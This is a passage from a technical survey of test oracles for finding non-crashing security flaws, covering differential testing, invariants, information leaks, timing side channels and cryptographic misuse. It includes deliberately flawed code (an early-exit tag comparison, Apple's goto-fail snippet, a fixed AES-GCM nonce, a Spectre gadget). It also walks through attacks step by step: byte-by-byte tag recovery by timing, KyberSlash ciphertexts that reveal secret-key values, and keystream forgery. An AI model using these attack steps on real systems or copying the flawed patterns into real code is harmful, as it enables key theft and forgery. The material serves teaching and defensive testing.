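- A disagreement is **durable** if at least one gateway forwards the input in a form that still makes two servers disagree. Many gateways tidy up a request before forwarding it, which makes the input useless for an attack.

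The study found 122 distinct disagreements. Developers had patched 68 of them, and Kallus and colleagues judged 39 exploitable. A disagreement does not prove a vulnerability, so a person still had to develop each one into an attack. Whether an attack works also depends on which programs are connected. For instance, many servers accept a line ending that the standard forbids in one part of a message. This would matter only behind a gateway that reads the line ending differently and forwards it unchanged, and Kallus and colleagues knew of no such gateway.

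Differential testing misses a bug that both programs share. Since version 3.6, Python's `int` function has accepted underscores between digits, so `1_000` means 1,000. The popular Python web servers AIOHTTP, Gunicorn and Tornado used `int` to read the size of each chunk of a message, so all three read the invalid size `0_ff` as 255. The gateway Apache Traffic Server read it as 0 and passed it on, which again let an attacker hide a request.

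A tester who compared only the three Python servers would have seen them agree completely. The HTTP Garden exposed the bug because it also includes servers written in other languages. Adding a fourth Python server would have helped less than adding one in C, although C's standard functions for reading numbers have their own quirks.

Comparing the outputs of two programs misses some flaws even when the programs are fully independent. A zero-knowledge virtual machine runs a program and produces a proof of the result that others can check without rerunning the program. A set of equations determines which proofs the checker accepts. If the equations are too loose, a dishonest prover can prove a false result, but an honest run still gives the right answer. *Revealing Semantic Gaps in Zero-Knowledge Virtual Machines via Obligation-Targeted Semantic Fuzzing* (2026) points out that comparing outputs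 therefore cannot reveal this flaw, however long the test runs. To find it, the tester has to tamper with the values behind a proof and see whether the checker still accepts them.

### Invariants

An invariant is a condition that should hold throughout a program's execution, or before and after every operation. The bank's `transfer` function should never create or destroy money, so the sum of all balances should stay the same:

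Σ balances after = Σ balances before.

A harness can calculate both sums and abort if they differ, which lets an ordinary crash oracle detect the flaw. Suppose that customer A has 100 and customer B has 50 before each of these calls:

| Call | A's balance after | B's balance after | Total | Invariant | Truth |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| A sends 30 to B | 70 | 80 | 150 | Holds | Correct |
| A sends 30 to A | 130 | 50 | 180 | Violated | Flaw: A has created money |
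| A sends −50 to B | 150 | 0 | 150 | Holds | Flaw: A has taken B's money |

The last call works because the function never checks that the amount is positive. Theft moves money without changing the total, so checking for conservation of money can't detect it. A second invariant would, such as one requiring that a customer's balance fall only when that customer has requested a payment. But someone has to think of that invariant, and a list of invariants doesn't show which ones are missing. The conservation check can also cause false alarms. If the bank pays interest from an account that the harness leaves out of the sum, every interest payment looks like new money.

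One way to find missing invariants is to compare a program with similar ones. *LogicScan* (2026) uses a language model to extract business rules from smart contracts already in use, which are programs that hold and transfer assets on a blockchain, then checks whether a new contract departs from those rules. It achieved an F1 score of 85.2%. Because LogicScan compares code instead of monitoring a run, the score doesn't show how well the same rules would work as a fuzzer's oracle. The method could also mistake a flaw that most contracts share for a rule, or flag an unusual but sound design as a violation.

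### Rules inferred by a language model

Carlini and colleagues state that Anthropic's Mythos Preview model can reliably distinguish what code is meant to do from what it does. They say it can recognize, for example, that a login function should admit only authorized users, even if the code contains a way around the login. If models can do this dependably, they could supply the missing specification for almost any program. But Carlini and colleagues give no error rate for logic bugs, and most of their examples were still secret because developers had not fixed them.

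In *Discovery or Memorization?*, Yang, Xu and colleagues (2026) measured something close to this ability. They collected 132 published business-logic flaws, disguised the applications' names and other clues, and asked six AI agents to find the flaws. The best, Claude Code with Opus 4.8, succeeded in 23% of its attempts, each limited to 20 minutes and $5. On a subset of 20 flaws, restoring the clues raised the agents' success rate from 21% to 41%. Some of the agents' apparent understanding of the developers' intentions may therefore be memory of published flaws. The strongest models released since would probably score higher.

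To score the agents, the researchers still needed a human-checked specification for every flaw. In Graylog, a log management program, ordinary users could create access tokens for their own accounts, but a flaw also let them create one for an administrator. The server's response looks the same in both cases, so the benchmark's oracle compares the user who made the request with the owner of the new token. The researchers knew to compare those two because they had read the advisory and the patch, which don't exist for unknown flaws.

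Code-Augur, which Luo, Zafar and colleagues (2026), in *CODE-AUGUR*, describe, makes a model write down its guesses and then tries to disprove them:

1. An agent reads the code and its documentation, and writes a threat model.
2. The agent examines one part of the program. If that part looks unsafe, the agent records a possible bug. If it looks safe, the agent adds an assertion stating the assumption behind that judgment.
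3. A fuzzer searches for an input that violates the assertion. For some numerical conditions, it gets feedback on how close it has come.
4. If the fuzzer succeeds, the agent decides whether the program is wrong or the assertion was too strict. In the second case it rewrites the assertion.

Luo and colleagues illustrate this with a bug in Little CMS, a library that converts colours between formats. The library records the number of colour channels in two places, and the two numbers should match. A function appears to check this, but a wildcard value bypasses the check, so a crafted file can set one number to 13 and the other to 1. The program runs normally until much later, when it reads past the end of a four-byte buffer and ASan reports the error. An assertion that the numbers match would fail as soon as they differ, which gives the fuzzer an easier target.

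In tests on known vulnerable software, Code-Augur found more bugs than Claude Code or Team Atlanta's ATLANTIS. All three used Claude Sonnet 4.6.

| Bugs found | Code-Augur | Claude Code | ATLANTIS |
|---|---|---|---|
| AIxCC projects: known bugs, of 39 | 33 | 32 | 25 |
| AIxCC projects: additional bugs | 26 | 12 | 11 |
| Recent open-source bugs: known, of 24 | 8 | 10 | 9 of 22 |
| Recent open-source bugs: additional | 50 | 26 | 20 |

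Code-Augur was no better than Claude Code at finding the known bugs, but it found more additional ones. It cost about $45 per audit, compared with $16 for Claude Code. Violated assertions led to 45 of its 117 findings (38%), though ordinary fuzzing or code review might have found some of those bugs anyway.

These benchmarks rely on reproducible crashes, so they show little about logic flaws. When Luo and colleagues audited other open-source projects, they dropped the crash requirement and checked each finding by hand. They reported 22 new vulnerabilities in seven projects, and developers had fixed or confirmed 16. About ten of the 22 involve no memory or arithmetic error. One is in chisel, a tool that forwards network connections and restricts which addresses each user may reach. Chisel accepted an address if any part of it matched the permitted pattern, so a rule that allowed `db:80` would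 also allow `db:8080`. Luo and colleagues do not say how many of the ten came from a violated assertion.

A model that infers a rule from faulty code may copy the fault. Code-Augur did this with gpsd, a program that reads data from satellite-navigation receivers. gpsd had room for 184 satellites, so Code-Augur inferred that the number of visible satellites should never exceed 184. The rule was useful at first, because malformed data could push the count higher and cause out-of-bounds reads. When the developers fixed only the loop that had crashed, the assertion that checked this rule still failed because other functions used the same unchecked count.

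Later, a valid input broke the inferred rule by pushing the count above 184, since one type of receiver can report up to 230 satellites. This revealed that the rule had repeated a mistaken limit in the code, which the developers raised to 230. If gpsd had silently discarded every satellite after the 184th, the program would always have obeyed the rule, and fuzzing could never have shown that the rule was wrong.

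The same could happen with `read_balance`. A model given only that function might infer that the account number must be between 0 and 2, because the code checks this and never checks the owner. An assertion of that range after the check would hold in every run, including the one in which user 7 reads user 9's balance. Code-Augur also uses the documentation, which would help here only if it stated who may see which account.

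## Information leaks and timing side channels

A program leaks information when it reveals something to a person whom a policy forbids from learning it. Some leaks also violate memory safety, as Heartbleed did, which is why ASan can detect it. In other leaks, the program makes only valid memory accesses but gives the data to the wrong person, so no sanitizer reports an error.

The Linux kernel's deliberate disclosure of one of its own addresses, described earlier, is one of these quieter leaks. The address does little harm alone, but it can be one step in a larger attack. Carlini and colleagues report that Anthropic's model built nearly a dozen working attacks on Linux by combining two to four vulnerabilities. One attack located the kernel in memory, read an important kernel structure, wrote to memory the kernel had already freed, and gained full control. A sanitizer could report the write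 to freed memory but not the deliberate disclosure of an address. The researchers don't say whether this attack used the disclosure described earlier. They withheld the details of that disclosure in April 2026 because it had no fix yet.

The model's attack on FreeBSD's file server also relied on a leak. To reach the buffer overflow described earlier, a request had to contain a handle based on the machine's ID and start-up time. Guessing could have taken about four billion attempts. But anyone can query the server for its full ID and the second its file service started, so a few guesses were enough. A tester writing a policy in advance would probably not have listed a server's start time as a secret.

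Secrets in logs are a more ordinary case. A program that writes a password to its log uses a valid string and a file it is allowed to write to. The harm comes later, when support staff or an intruder reads the log.

### Noninterference as a two-run test

Let *p* be a program's public inputs, *s* its secret inputs and *O*(*p*, *s*) everything an attacker can observe. A deterministic program satisfies noninterference if, for every *p* and every pair of secrets *s*₁ and *s*₂,

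*O*(*p*, *s*₁) = *O*(*p*, *s*₂).

A harness can test this equation by comparing two runs. *KyberSlash* (Bernstein, Bhargavan and colleagues, 2025) calls this ideal "secret independence" and includes running time and memory accesses in what an attacker may observe.

Suppose a staff website shows Ana the average salary in her team, which is just her and Ben. Ana knows her own salary, so it counts as public here, and Ben's is secret.

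| Run | Ana's salary | Ben's salary | Average shown |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 50,000 | 60,000 | 55,000 |
| 2 | 50,000 | 80,000 | 65,000 |

The averages differ, so the page violates noninterference. Ana can double the average and subtract her own salary to get Ben's. Searching the page for Ben's salary would not have revealed the leak, because the figure never appears there.

The test is often too strict. In a team of 50, raising Ben's salary by 20,000 changes the average by 400, which is still a violation, although the company may be happy to publish that average. A login page also has to reveal whether a guess was right. The tester therefore needs to define *D*(*p*, *s*), the information that the program may release, and require equal observations only when that information is equal:

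*D*(*p*, *s*₁) = *D*(*p*, *s*₂) ⇒ *O*(*p*, *s*₁) = *O*(*p*, *s*₂).

For the login page, the same wrong guess should therefore produce the same observations whatever the real password is. The harness also has to keep any random numbers and clock values the same across runs.

If two runs that differ only in the secret produce different results, the results depend on the secret. Matching results are only weak evidence of independence, because another pair of secrets might have produced different ones.

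### Following secrets with taint tracking

Taint tracking looks for leaks in a single run by following marked data to forbidden sinks. Anota uses it for its password rule and also lets developers mark a function, so that everything the function returns is marked.

The results can differ from those of a two-run test. For example, Anota's rule allows a hashed password in the log, but a two-run test would report the same log unless the tester had accounted for the hashing, because different passwords have different hashes.

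Taint tracking can miss secrets that affect only which code runs:

```python
if password.startswith("a"):
    log.write("type 1")
else:
    log.write("type 2")
```

Neither message contains any part of the password, so a tracker that follows only computed values reports nothing. But two runs with the passwords `apple` and `plum` would produce different logs. A tracker can mark everything that happens after a branch on a secret, but then it marks a lot of harmless data too. It can also report a value that carries no information, such as a secret number multiplied by zero.

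### Excess data in web responses

Web services often send a browser more data than the page displays, and anyone can read the full response with the browser's own tools. *Mockingbird* (Xia, Sun and colleagues, 2025) gives an example from Microsoft's CMT, a system for submitting conference papers. Its responses included a status field that let authors learn the outcome of peer review early.

This flaw is called excessive data exposure, and *EDEFuzz* (2024) presents a fuzzer for it. The fuzzer assumes that a field is probably unnecessary if removing it doesn't change the page:

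1. A tester loads a page and performs the actions that trigger a request. EDEFuzz records the actions and the server's responses.
2. A simulated server replays the responses to a browser, but with one field deleted.
3. EDEFuzz compares the new page with the original, ignoring details that vary between identical replays.
4. If the pages match, EDEFuzz reports the field. It then repeats the process with the next one.

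If *R* is the response and *d* a field in it, EDEFuzz reports *d* when

Page(*R*) = Page(*R* without *d*).

Like the noninterference test, this compares two runs, but here a match is the sign of a problem.

One of its findings was in a parcel-tracking page. The page showed the driver's position only to the customer whose parcel was next, but the server's response always included the driver's position, speed and direction. A customer could have followed the van and worked out where other people lived. The response also contained contact details for the driver's manager.

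In a controlled study, 98.65% of the fields EDEFuzz reported were unused. Its developers also tried it on 69 applications from a list of the 200 most popular websites, but it stopped on nine because their pages changed structure between identical replays. On one retailer's site, the page used only 4.4% of the fields it received. Across their experiments, the developers found five leaks serious enough to disclose immediately. Unused data isn't necessarily sensitive, so a person still has to judge each field.

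The rule has false positives, such as a field that the page needs only after another click. It can also miss leaks. Some retailers send the exact number of items in stock to a page that displays only "low stock". If the page calculates that label from the number, deleting the number changes the page, so the rule treats it as necessary. Changing the number from 3 to 4 would be a better test, because the label would stay the same. The rule also misses any secret that the page displays, such as another customer's balance.

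Wang and colleagues point out that EDEFuzz needs a rendered web page, which many services don't have. EDEFuzz is also slow because it reloads the page for every field, which can take hours or days for a response with thousands of fields. Xia and colleagues instead track each field through the page's JavaScript and report those that never reach the screen, the browser's storage or another expected use. On eight open-source applications, their tool was nearly 20 times faster than EDEFuzz and improved F1 by 24.1%. Xia and colleagues chose the applications themselves, so the comparison needs repeating on applications that someone else chose.

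### Recovering a secret from time

A message authentication code, or MAC, is a short tag that proves a message came from someone who knows a secret key. The server calculates the correct tag for each message it receives and compares it with the tag the sender supplied. ImperialViolet's *Checking that functions are constant time with Valgrind* (2010) describes a faulty comparison of two 16-byte tags, which works like this:

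```c
int same_tag(const uint8_t *correct, const uint8_t *guess)
{
    int pos = 0;
    while (pos < 16 && correct[pos] == guess[pos])
        pos++;
    return pos == 16;
}
```

The function returns the right answer for every input, but it stops comparing at the first wrong byte. Suppose a check takes 500 nanoseconds plus 2 more for each byte compared, and the correct tag for the attacker's forged message begins with `7C 3E`.

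| Guess begins | Bytes compared | Time | What the attacker learns |
|---|---|---|---|
| `00 00 00` | 1 | 502 ns | The first byte isn't `00` |
| `7C 00 00` | 2 | 504 ns | The first byte is `7C` |
| `7C 3E 00` | 3 | 506 ns | The second byte is `3E` |

The attacker tries up to 256 values for the first byte, keeps the one the server takes longest to reject, and moves on to the next byte. The last byte is right when the server accepts the tag. The whole tag takes at most 16 × 256 = 4,096 different guesses. If the comparison took the same time for every wrong tag, the attacker would have to search 2¹²⁸ possibilities, or about 3.4 × 10³⁸.

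Real timings vary for many other reasons, so the attacker repeats each guess and averages the results. With 10,000 repetitions per guess and 1,000 requests a second, the attack would take about 11 hours.

A safer function compares all 16 bytes, collects any differences in one variable and checks that variable only at the end. Both versions return the same answers, so a functional test can't distinguish them.

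### Measuring time with dudect

*Dude, is my code constant time?* (Reparaz, Balasch and Verbauwhede, 2016) introduced dudect, which looks for timing leaks by measuring execution time. It runs a function many times on inputs from two classes, in random order. Usually one class repeats a fixed input and the other contains random inputs. dudect then tests whether the two classes' average times differ by more than chance would explain.

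For classes *A* and *B*, let *x̄* be the average time, *s* the standard deviation (a measure of how much the times vary) and *n* the number of measurements. Welch's *t* statistic is

*t* = (*x̄*_A − *x̄*_B) / √(*s*_A²/*n*_A + *s*_B²/*n*_B).

In the example above, suppose that the fixed guess has the first byte right and averages 504 ns. Random guesses nearly always fail at the first byte and average about 502 ns. The standard deviation is 50 ns in both classes. With 10,000 measurements of each,

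*t* = 2 / √(2,500/10,000 + 2,500/10,000) = 2 / 0.707 ≈ 2.8.

That is weak evidence. With a million measurements of each, the denominator falls to 0.0707 and *t* rises to about 28. Taking a hundred times as many measurements makes *t* ten times as large if the difference is real, but *t* stays near zero if there is no difference.

Reparaz and colleagues treat a value above 5 as very likely a leak, though the tool waits for 10 before it reports that the code is probably not constant time. Their published examples show how much the required effort varies:

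| Code under test | Measurements | Largest *t* |
|---|---|---|
| Comparison with C's standard `memcmp` | 370,000 | 1,271 |
| A version of the AES cipher that uses lookup tables | 590,000 | 561 |
| Elliptic-curve code with a deliberate leak | About 20,000 | 24 |
| Constant-time comparison | 71 million | 2.8 |

The choice of input classes matters even more than the number of measurements. In the tag example, dudect would need the following number of measurements per class to reach *t* = 10:

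| Fixed guess | Average time | Measurements needed |
|---|---|---|
| First byte wrong | 502 ns | About 8 billion |
| First byte right, second wrong | 504 ns | About 125,000 |
| First 15 bytes right, last wrong | 532 ns | About 560 |

A tester who picked a fixed guess with the wrong first byte would almost certainly conclude that the function was safe. Reparaz and colleagues therefore recommend using knowledge of the code to design inputs, and they warn that passing the test doesn't prove that code is constant-time.

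dudect also treats the function as a black box. CRoCS, a research group at Masaryk University, notes that it will miss code that takes different paths of exactly equal duration. Such code may still leak through the processor's cache, a small fast memory that keeps recently used data, because the two paths use different addresses.

### Marking secrets with ctgrind

ctgrind examines what the code does instead of how long it takes. Its author, Adam Langley, wanted to find two operations that commonly make running time depend on a secret: branching on it, and using it to calculate a memory address. That requires a record of which bits in memory derive from secrets.

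Valgrind's Memcheck tool already keeps such a record for uninitialised memory. It follows uninitialised bits through calculations and warns when the program branches on them or uses them in an address. Langley therefore tells Memcheck that the secret is uninitialised. For `same_tag`, the process is:

1. The test program fills both tags with ordinary values, then marks `correct` as uninitialised.
2. The function compares `correct[0]` with `guess[0]`. Memcheck marks the result as uninitialised because it depends on `correct[0]`.
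3. The loop branches on that result, and Memcheck warns of a jump that depends on uninitialised values.

This is taint tracking with branches and memory addresses as the sinks, and it needs neither a second secret nor timing measurements. Bitcoin ABC's *valgrind_ctime_test.c File Reference*, which documents such a test for a signature library, notes that one secret should in theory be enough, because any control flow that depends on it would cause an error. But Memcheck checks only the code that runs, so a test still has to reach every path.

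In his first trials, Langley found a secret-dependent memory access in an OpenSSL function with "consttime" in its name. In a code comment, the developers had claimed only that the function limited such leaks. BoringSSL's *Add start of infrastructure for checking constant-time properties* explains that ctgrind's patch is now obsolete because Valgrind has its own commands for marking memory. BoringSSL, Google's version of OpenSSL, uses those commands directly. TIMECOP, a newer tool, applies the same method to large collections of cryptographic code.

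Microwalk runs a program with many different secrets, records the branches and memory addresses in each run, and compares the recordings. This is a two-run noninterference test in which *O* is the recording instead of the output or the time. Random delays don't affect it, and it can detect secret-dependent paths that dudect would miss because they take the same time. Unlike ctgrind, it finds a leak only if the tester tries secrets that make the program behave differently. It can also estimate how much information the differences reveal.

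ctgrind and Microwalk both enforce a stricter rule than equal running time. Mbed TLS's *Tools for testing constant-flow code* calls code that obeys it constant-flow. The rule doesn't cover everything, however. Langley's post assumes that each basic processor instruction takes constant time, which it describes as true for "all sane CPUs". Division is an exception on many processors.

### KyberSlash

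Kyber is a method for two parties to agree on a secret key, and it should resist attacks by quantum computers. The US standards institute NIST has standardised it as ML-KEM. One party encrypts a random message with the other's public key, and the receiver recovers it with a long-term secret key. Both then derive the shared key from that message.

During decryption, the receiver calculates 256 numbers from 0 to 3,328 and rounds each to a single bit. In the official reference code of November 2023, this step amounted to the following, where `t` is one of the numbers:

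```c
bit = ((2*t + 1664) / 3329) & 1;
```

The numerator depends on the secret key, though the code contains no secret-dependent branch or memory address. Compilers usually replace division by a constant with a faster multiplication, but GCC generally keeps the division when a developer asks for small code with `-Os`.

Bernstein and colleagues attacked this code on a Raspberry Pi 2. Division there takes 20 cycles longer once the numerator reaches 3,329, with further increases of two cycles at 4,096 and one at 8,192. The attacker sends a specially made ciphertext for which one of the 256 numbers is

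*t* = (208 − 72*s*) mod 3329,

where *s* is one number in the secret key, between −3 and 3.

| Secret *s* | *t* | Numerator 2*t* + 1664 | Extra cycles |
|---|---|---|---|
| −3 | 424 | 2,512 | 0 |
| 0 | 208 | 2,080 | 0 |
| 2 | 64 | 1,792 | 0 |
| 3 | 3,321 | 8,306 | 23 |

The values of *s* left out of the table also give fast responses, so a slow response means that *s* is 3. Replacing 72 with −72 singles out −3, and replacing it with 107 separates 2 and 3 from the rest. The attacker repeats this for all 512 numbers in the key of Kyber's smallest version, taking many measurements to average out noise. The attack recovered the full key in all ten experiments, which took two to four hours each.

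This leak is called KyberSlash1. A related leak, KyberSlash2, comes from the divisions used to compress a ciphertext. KyberSlash2 revealed a full key in about four minutes on a small Arm Cortex-M4 processor.

Several kinds of check had missed the problem:

| Check | What it examines | Result for the division |
|---|---|---|
| Functional tests | Whether both parties get the same key | Pass, because the answer is right at any speed |
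| ASan and UndefinedBehaviorSanitizer | Memory accesses and undefined operations | Pass, because the division is valid |
| ctgrind's original rule | Secret-dependent branches and addresses | No warning about a division instruction |
| Inspecting code compiled for speed | Whether a division instruction remains | Usually pass, because the compiler has replaced it |

Some of the researchers found KyberSlash1 while trying to prove that a Rust version of Kyber was correct. They translated the Rust code into F\*, a language whose types can separate secret integers from public ones. Its library defines no division for secret integers, so the type checker rejected the line that divided one.

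The same check missed KyberSlash2 at first because the researchers had labelled ciphertexts as public. That label is correct for a ciphertext that Kyber sends, but the receiver also re-encrypts the recovered message to check that the original ciphertext was valid, and the result can reveal the secret key. When the researchers corrected the label, the type checker found the flaw.

Bernstein and colleagues then modified Valgrind to warn when a secret reaches a division instruction. The modified version found all the KyberSlash divisions in code compiled with `-Os`. They also ran it on nearly 1,300 cryptographic implementations in 87 minutes on a 128-core machine. The only divisions it reported there were in New Hope, an ancestor of Kyber.

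### Compilers and processors

A developer can't permanently fix KyberSlash by choosing the right compiler option. On 32-bit MIPS processors, GCC 14.1 keeps the division even when it optimises for speed. By contrast, one of dudect's sample programs leaks when compiled without optimisation, but a few million measurements of the optimised version showed no leak.

Bernstein and colleagues warn that compilers can also turn branch-free masking operations into conditional jumps. The F\* check can't detect this because it examines only the source. Valgrind examines the compiled program, so it can detect the jumps, but its result applies only to that build. In the large test, the New Hope divisions appeared with GCC's `-Os` option but not with Clang's. A project therefore has to test the builds it ships.

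The processor can leak secrets even when the compiled code looks safe. Spectre attacks exploit speculative execution, in which a processor guesses the outcome of a branch and runs ahead. Consider this code:

```c
if (i < 16)
    y = table[data[i] * 64];
```

If *i* is 1,000, the program should read nothing. But the processor may predict that the condition is true, read `data[1000]` and load the matching part of `table`. It then detects the mistake and discards the result, but the loaded part of `table` stays in the cache. An attacker who can time later accesses to `table` can find which part loads quickly and work out the value of `data[1000]`.

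The processor discards the result of the bad speculative read, so ASan does not report it. ctgrind and Microwalk follow only the path whose results the processor kept.

The Hertzbleed attack exploits processors that change speed according to how much power they draw. Power use depends on the data, so even code that executes the same instructions at the same addresses can take different times for different secrets.

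*SILENT* (Dunsche, Erinola and colleagues, 2025) cites Spectre and Hertzbleed as reasons to measure finished software as well as check its code. Measurement suits Hertzbleed better, because the leak affects the program's own running time. Spectre leaves its evidence in the cache, so timing the vulnerable function alone may not reveal it.

### False alarms and leaks too small to exploit

A tool that tracks secrets will warn about some that no longer need protection. BoringSSL's developers got such a warning in their RSA code, where a safety check compares a decrypted message with a public number. Valgrind warned about the branch because the message is secret, although the check always has the same outcome when decryption works properly. Valgrind also warns about a loop in Kyber's code that discards unsuitable random values. One version of Kyber avoids the warning with an extra line stating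 that the result of the loop's check is public.

Such statements are small pieces of policy, and they take time to write. When Bernstein and colleagues extended their Valgrind test to every key-exchange method of Kyber's type in the collection, it produced 11,610 warnings about variable-time instructions, from 556 lines of code in 139 implementations. The researchers examined only a couple of examples and stress that a warning doesn't establish an exploitable leak.

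Statistical tools can also raise false alarms because most assume that each measurement is independent, when one run can change the cache and so affect the next. An earlier tool reported a leak in Mbed TLS that researchers could not confirm by reading the code. Dunsche and colleagues found strong correlation between the measurements, which probably explains the report. Worries about reliability also discourage developers from using these tools. In a survey that Dunsche and colleagues cite, more than 60% of participants used no tool for checking constant-time code.

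Even an accurate test can report a leak too small to matter, because with enough measurements it will eventually detect any difference at all. SILENT, the tool from Dunsche and colleagues, lets a developer choose a negligible difference Δ. It compares quantiles, such as the time that 10% of runs fall below, and reports a leak only if the evidence shows that

max |*q*_A − *q*_B| > Δ,

where *q*_A and *q*_B are matching quantiles of the two classes. This also detects inputs that have the same average time but vary by different amounts, which dudect's test on averages would miss.

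The threshold Δ is hard to choose. One group of researchers considered differences below 100 ns unexploitable, while another researcher argues that a single clock cycle can be detectable over a local network. Dunsche and colleagues tried both thresholds in SILENT on KyberSlash, whose leak they expected to be around 20 cycles. SILENT reported the leak with the one-cycle threshold but not with the 100 ns one.

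Bernstein and colleagues recovered whole keys on the 900 MHz Raspberry Pi, where 20 cycles last only 22 ns. Their attack ran on the same processor as the victim, so it doesn't refute the 100 ns figure for attacks over a network. OpenSSL's security policy excludes attacks that require access to the same machine, but a cloud company whose customers share processors could not reasonably exclude them. Δ therefore depends on the threat model, as does the value of a report from a fuzz harness. In tacet, a newer Rust tool, the developer specifies the threat model by choosing an attacker, such as one on a neighbouring network, according to Rust Digger's copy of its documentation.

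Noise makes each measurement less useful to an attacker. *A Statistical Side-Channel Risk Model for Timing Variability in Lattice-Based Post-Quantum Cryptography* (2025) estimates that one kind of cache leak in Kyber reveals 0.18 bits of information on an idle machine and 0.01 bits on a busy one. But an attacker can often compensate by taking more measurements. Bernstein and colleagues' KyberSlash2 attack needed 6,144 decryptions when they measured the timing on the target device. When they measured it from a second device connected by wires, the attack needed 24,576 decryptions and about 20 minutes, but it still recovered the key in all ten attempts.

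## Cryptographic flaws and misuse

Cryptographic code can also fail in ways unrelated to timing. A library can compute the wrong answer, a protocol can accept something it should reject, and an application can misuse a library that works correctly. These failures normally produce no error.

### A library that computes the wrong answer

AES-SIV is a method of encryption that also produces a 16-byte tag, which the receiver recomputes to detect tampering. The sender calculates the tag as

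*V* = S2V(*K*₁, *A*, *P*),

where S2V is a keyed function, *K*₁ is half of the secret key, *P* is the message and *A* is optional extra data, such as a header. The tag also determines the keystream, a string of random-looking bytes that the sender combines with the message by XOR (written ⊕).

Anthropic's *ANT-2026-BT210RQ0 · libtom/libtomcrypt* describes a flaw that the company's AI model Claude found in libtomcrypt, a C library. If the caller supplied no extra data, libtomcrypt left the plaintext out of the tag calculation, so every message encrypted under the same key had the same tag and keystream.

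An attacker who knows the plaintext of one message can compute the keystream. If the letter A (41 in hexadecimal) became the byte 9C, the keystream byte is 41 ⊕ 9C = DD. To forge a B (42), the attacker sends 42 ⊕ DD = 9F with the old tag, and the receiver accepts the forgery.

The library's own test encrypted and decrypted 1,000 times without extra data and checked that decryption returned the original plaintext. The check always passed because encryption and decryption had the same bug. The constant tag also hid a bug in the test itself, so the test failed once the library was corrected.

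### A protocol that accepts what it should reject

The TLS protocol protects most web traffic. In many TLS connections, the server sends its certificate, which contains a long-term public key, and then a temporary key signed with the matching private key. The client must check that signature. Certificates are public, so without this check anyone on the network could present a bank's real certificate alongside their own temporary key.

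Until February 2014, Apple's code for this check contained a repeated line. Slightly shortened, it read:

```c
if ((err = SSLHashSHA1.update(&hashCtx, &signedParams)) != 0)
    goto fail;
    goto fail;
if ((err = SSLHashSHA1.final(&hashCtx, &hashOut)) != 0)
    goto fail;
err = sslRawVerify(/* key, hash, signature */);
fail:
    return err;
```

The `if` controls only the first `goto fail`. The second always runs, so the program jumps past `sslRawVerify`, the call that checks the signature. At that point `err` is still 0, which means success, so the function accepts any signature.

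The flaw (CVE-2014-1266) became known as "goto fail". An honest server's signature is valid, so the function returned the correct result on every normal connection. Adam Langley, ctgrind's author, noted at the time that testing for the flaw was hard because it required a TLS server that could deliberately misbehave deep inside the handshake.

### An application that misuses a correct library

This Python function encrypts text with AES-GCM, another method that produces a tag:

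```python
NONCE = b"\x00" * 12

def save(key, text):
    return AESGCM(key).encrypt(NONCE, text, None)
```

PentesterLab's *Playing Tag with GCM* (2026) explains that a program must never use the same nonce twice with one key. Here the nonce is always twelve zero bytes, so two messages under one key share a keystream, much as they did in libtomcrypt. An attacker can also recover enough information to forge tags. But the library did what the caller asked, and no single call is wrong.

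A key written into the source code also triggers no crash or sanitizer report. Switching off certificate checks can make a test suite more reliable, because connections no longer fail when a test server's certificate expires. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-44467* (2026) describes a subtler flaw in Anthropic's Claude Desktop, whose feature for working on remote machines checked whether a server's name was in the user's list of known hosts but never compared the server's key with the one stored there.

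| Flaw | Ordinary test | Result | What exposes the flaw |
|---|---|---|---|
| AES-SIV tag | Encrypt, decrypt, compare | Pass | A tag known to be correct |
| "goto fail" | Connect to an honest server | Pass | A server that sends a bad signature |
| Fixed nonce | Encrypt, decrypt, compare | Pass | The nonces from two calls |

### The OpenSSL carry bug

Some cryptography requires computing *a*^*b* mod *c* for numbers hundreds of digits long. A processor handles them in 64-bit words and carries from one word to the next, as people do with digits on paper. If a program adds 1 to 199 and loses the carry out of the tens column, it gets 100. In binary, a carry passes through a 64-bit word only if all its bits are 1, which happens in random data about once in 1.8 × 10¹⁹ words. Ordinary tests can easily miss a mistake in handling such a rare carry.

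OpenSSL's developers wrote a harness, *bignum.c* (2016), to look for wrong results. It takes random *a*, *b* and *c*, calculates the answer with both a fast method and a naive one, and aborts if the two answers differ.

OSS-Fuzz ran this harness and found a carry bug in the fast squaring code for 64-bit Intel and AMD processors (CVE-2017-3732). In May 2017, Google cited the bug to show that fuzzing can find correctness errors as well as memory errors. That August, OSS-Fuzz reported another carry bug, which OpenSSL called very similar, though it affected only newer processors. *Fuzzing Math*, from The Fuzzing Project, describes a 2015 carry bug in the same function.

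Without the comparison, the same fuzzer would almost certainly have missed the bug, because the wrong number did not crash the program. Nobody seems to have published a run that tests this.

GCVE (2017) describes attacks on RSA as very difficult and unlikely, and attacks on Diffie–Hellman key exchange as "just feasible" for an attacker with very large resources.

### Test vectors built around known mistakes

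A test vector is an input with its correct output. Standards usually include a few, mostly for valid inputs. Google's Project Wycheproof, released in December 2016, collects inputs that past implementations got wrong. Each vector is marked valid, invalid or acceptable, and "acceptable" is for cases that reasonable libraries handle differently. Many vectors also have a label naming the mistake they test for. Google said at the release that more than 80 test cases had uncovered more than 40 security bugs.

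One of Wycheproof's tests concerns a digital signature made of two numbers, *r* and *s*. Both must be at least 1, and a verifier that doesn't check this may accept a signature of two zeros for any message. Anthropic's *ANT-2026-KNXJMVYC · wolfssl/wolfssl* describes this mistake in wolfSSL, a TLS library popular in small devices. wolfSSL already checked the range for the common ECDSA signatures but not for the rarer ECCSI signatures. An old mistake can thus survive in an algorithm if nobody has run the equivalent test on it.

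Test vectors also check only the interface they are run through. wolfSSL had a working tag check for the ChaCha20-Poly1305 cipher, but it also offers a second set of functions that imitate OpenSSL's. Anthropic's *ANT-2026-RSSMAMA7 · wolfssl/wolfssl* explains that these computed the tag, wrote it over the one the sender had supplied, and reported success without comparing the two. A test vector with a false tag would have exposed the flaw, but only if run through the second set of functions. The fix includes such a test, with a tag of all zeros.

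Test vectors can also miss flaws that appear only in very long messages. Anthropic's disclosure dashboard (2026) lists a wolfSSL flaw in which a 32-bit counter wraps around and lets an attacker forge the authentication code of a message longer than 4 gigabytes. Test vector files are unlikely to include a message that long.

### Comparing libraries

Differential testing suits cryptography because many libraries implement the same algorithms. Cryptofuzz, which Guido Vranken began in 2019, picks an operation, a key and a message from the fuzzer's input, runs them through every library that supports the operation, and aborts if the results differ. Cryptofuzz can't detect a repeated nonce, because correct libraries all produce the same ciphertext for the second message.

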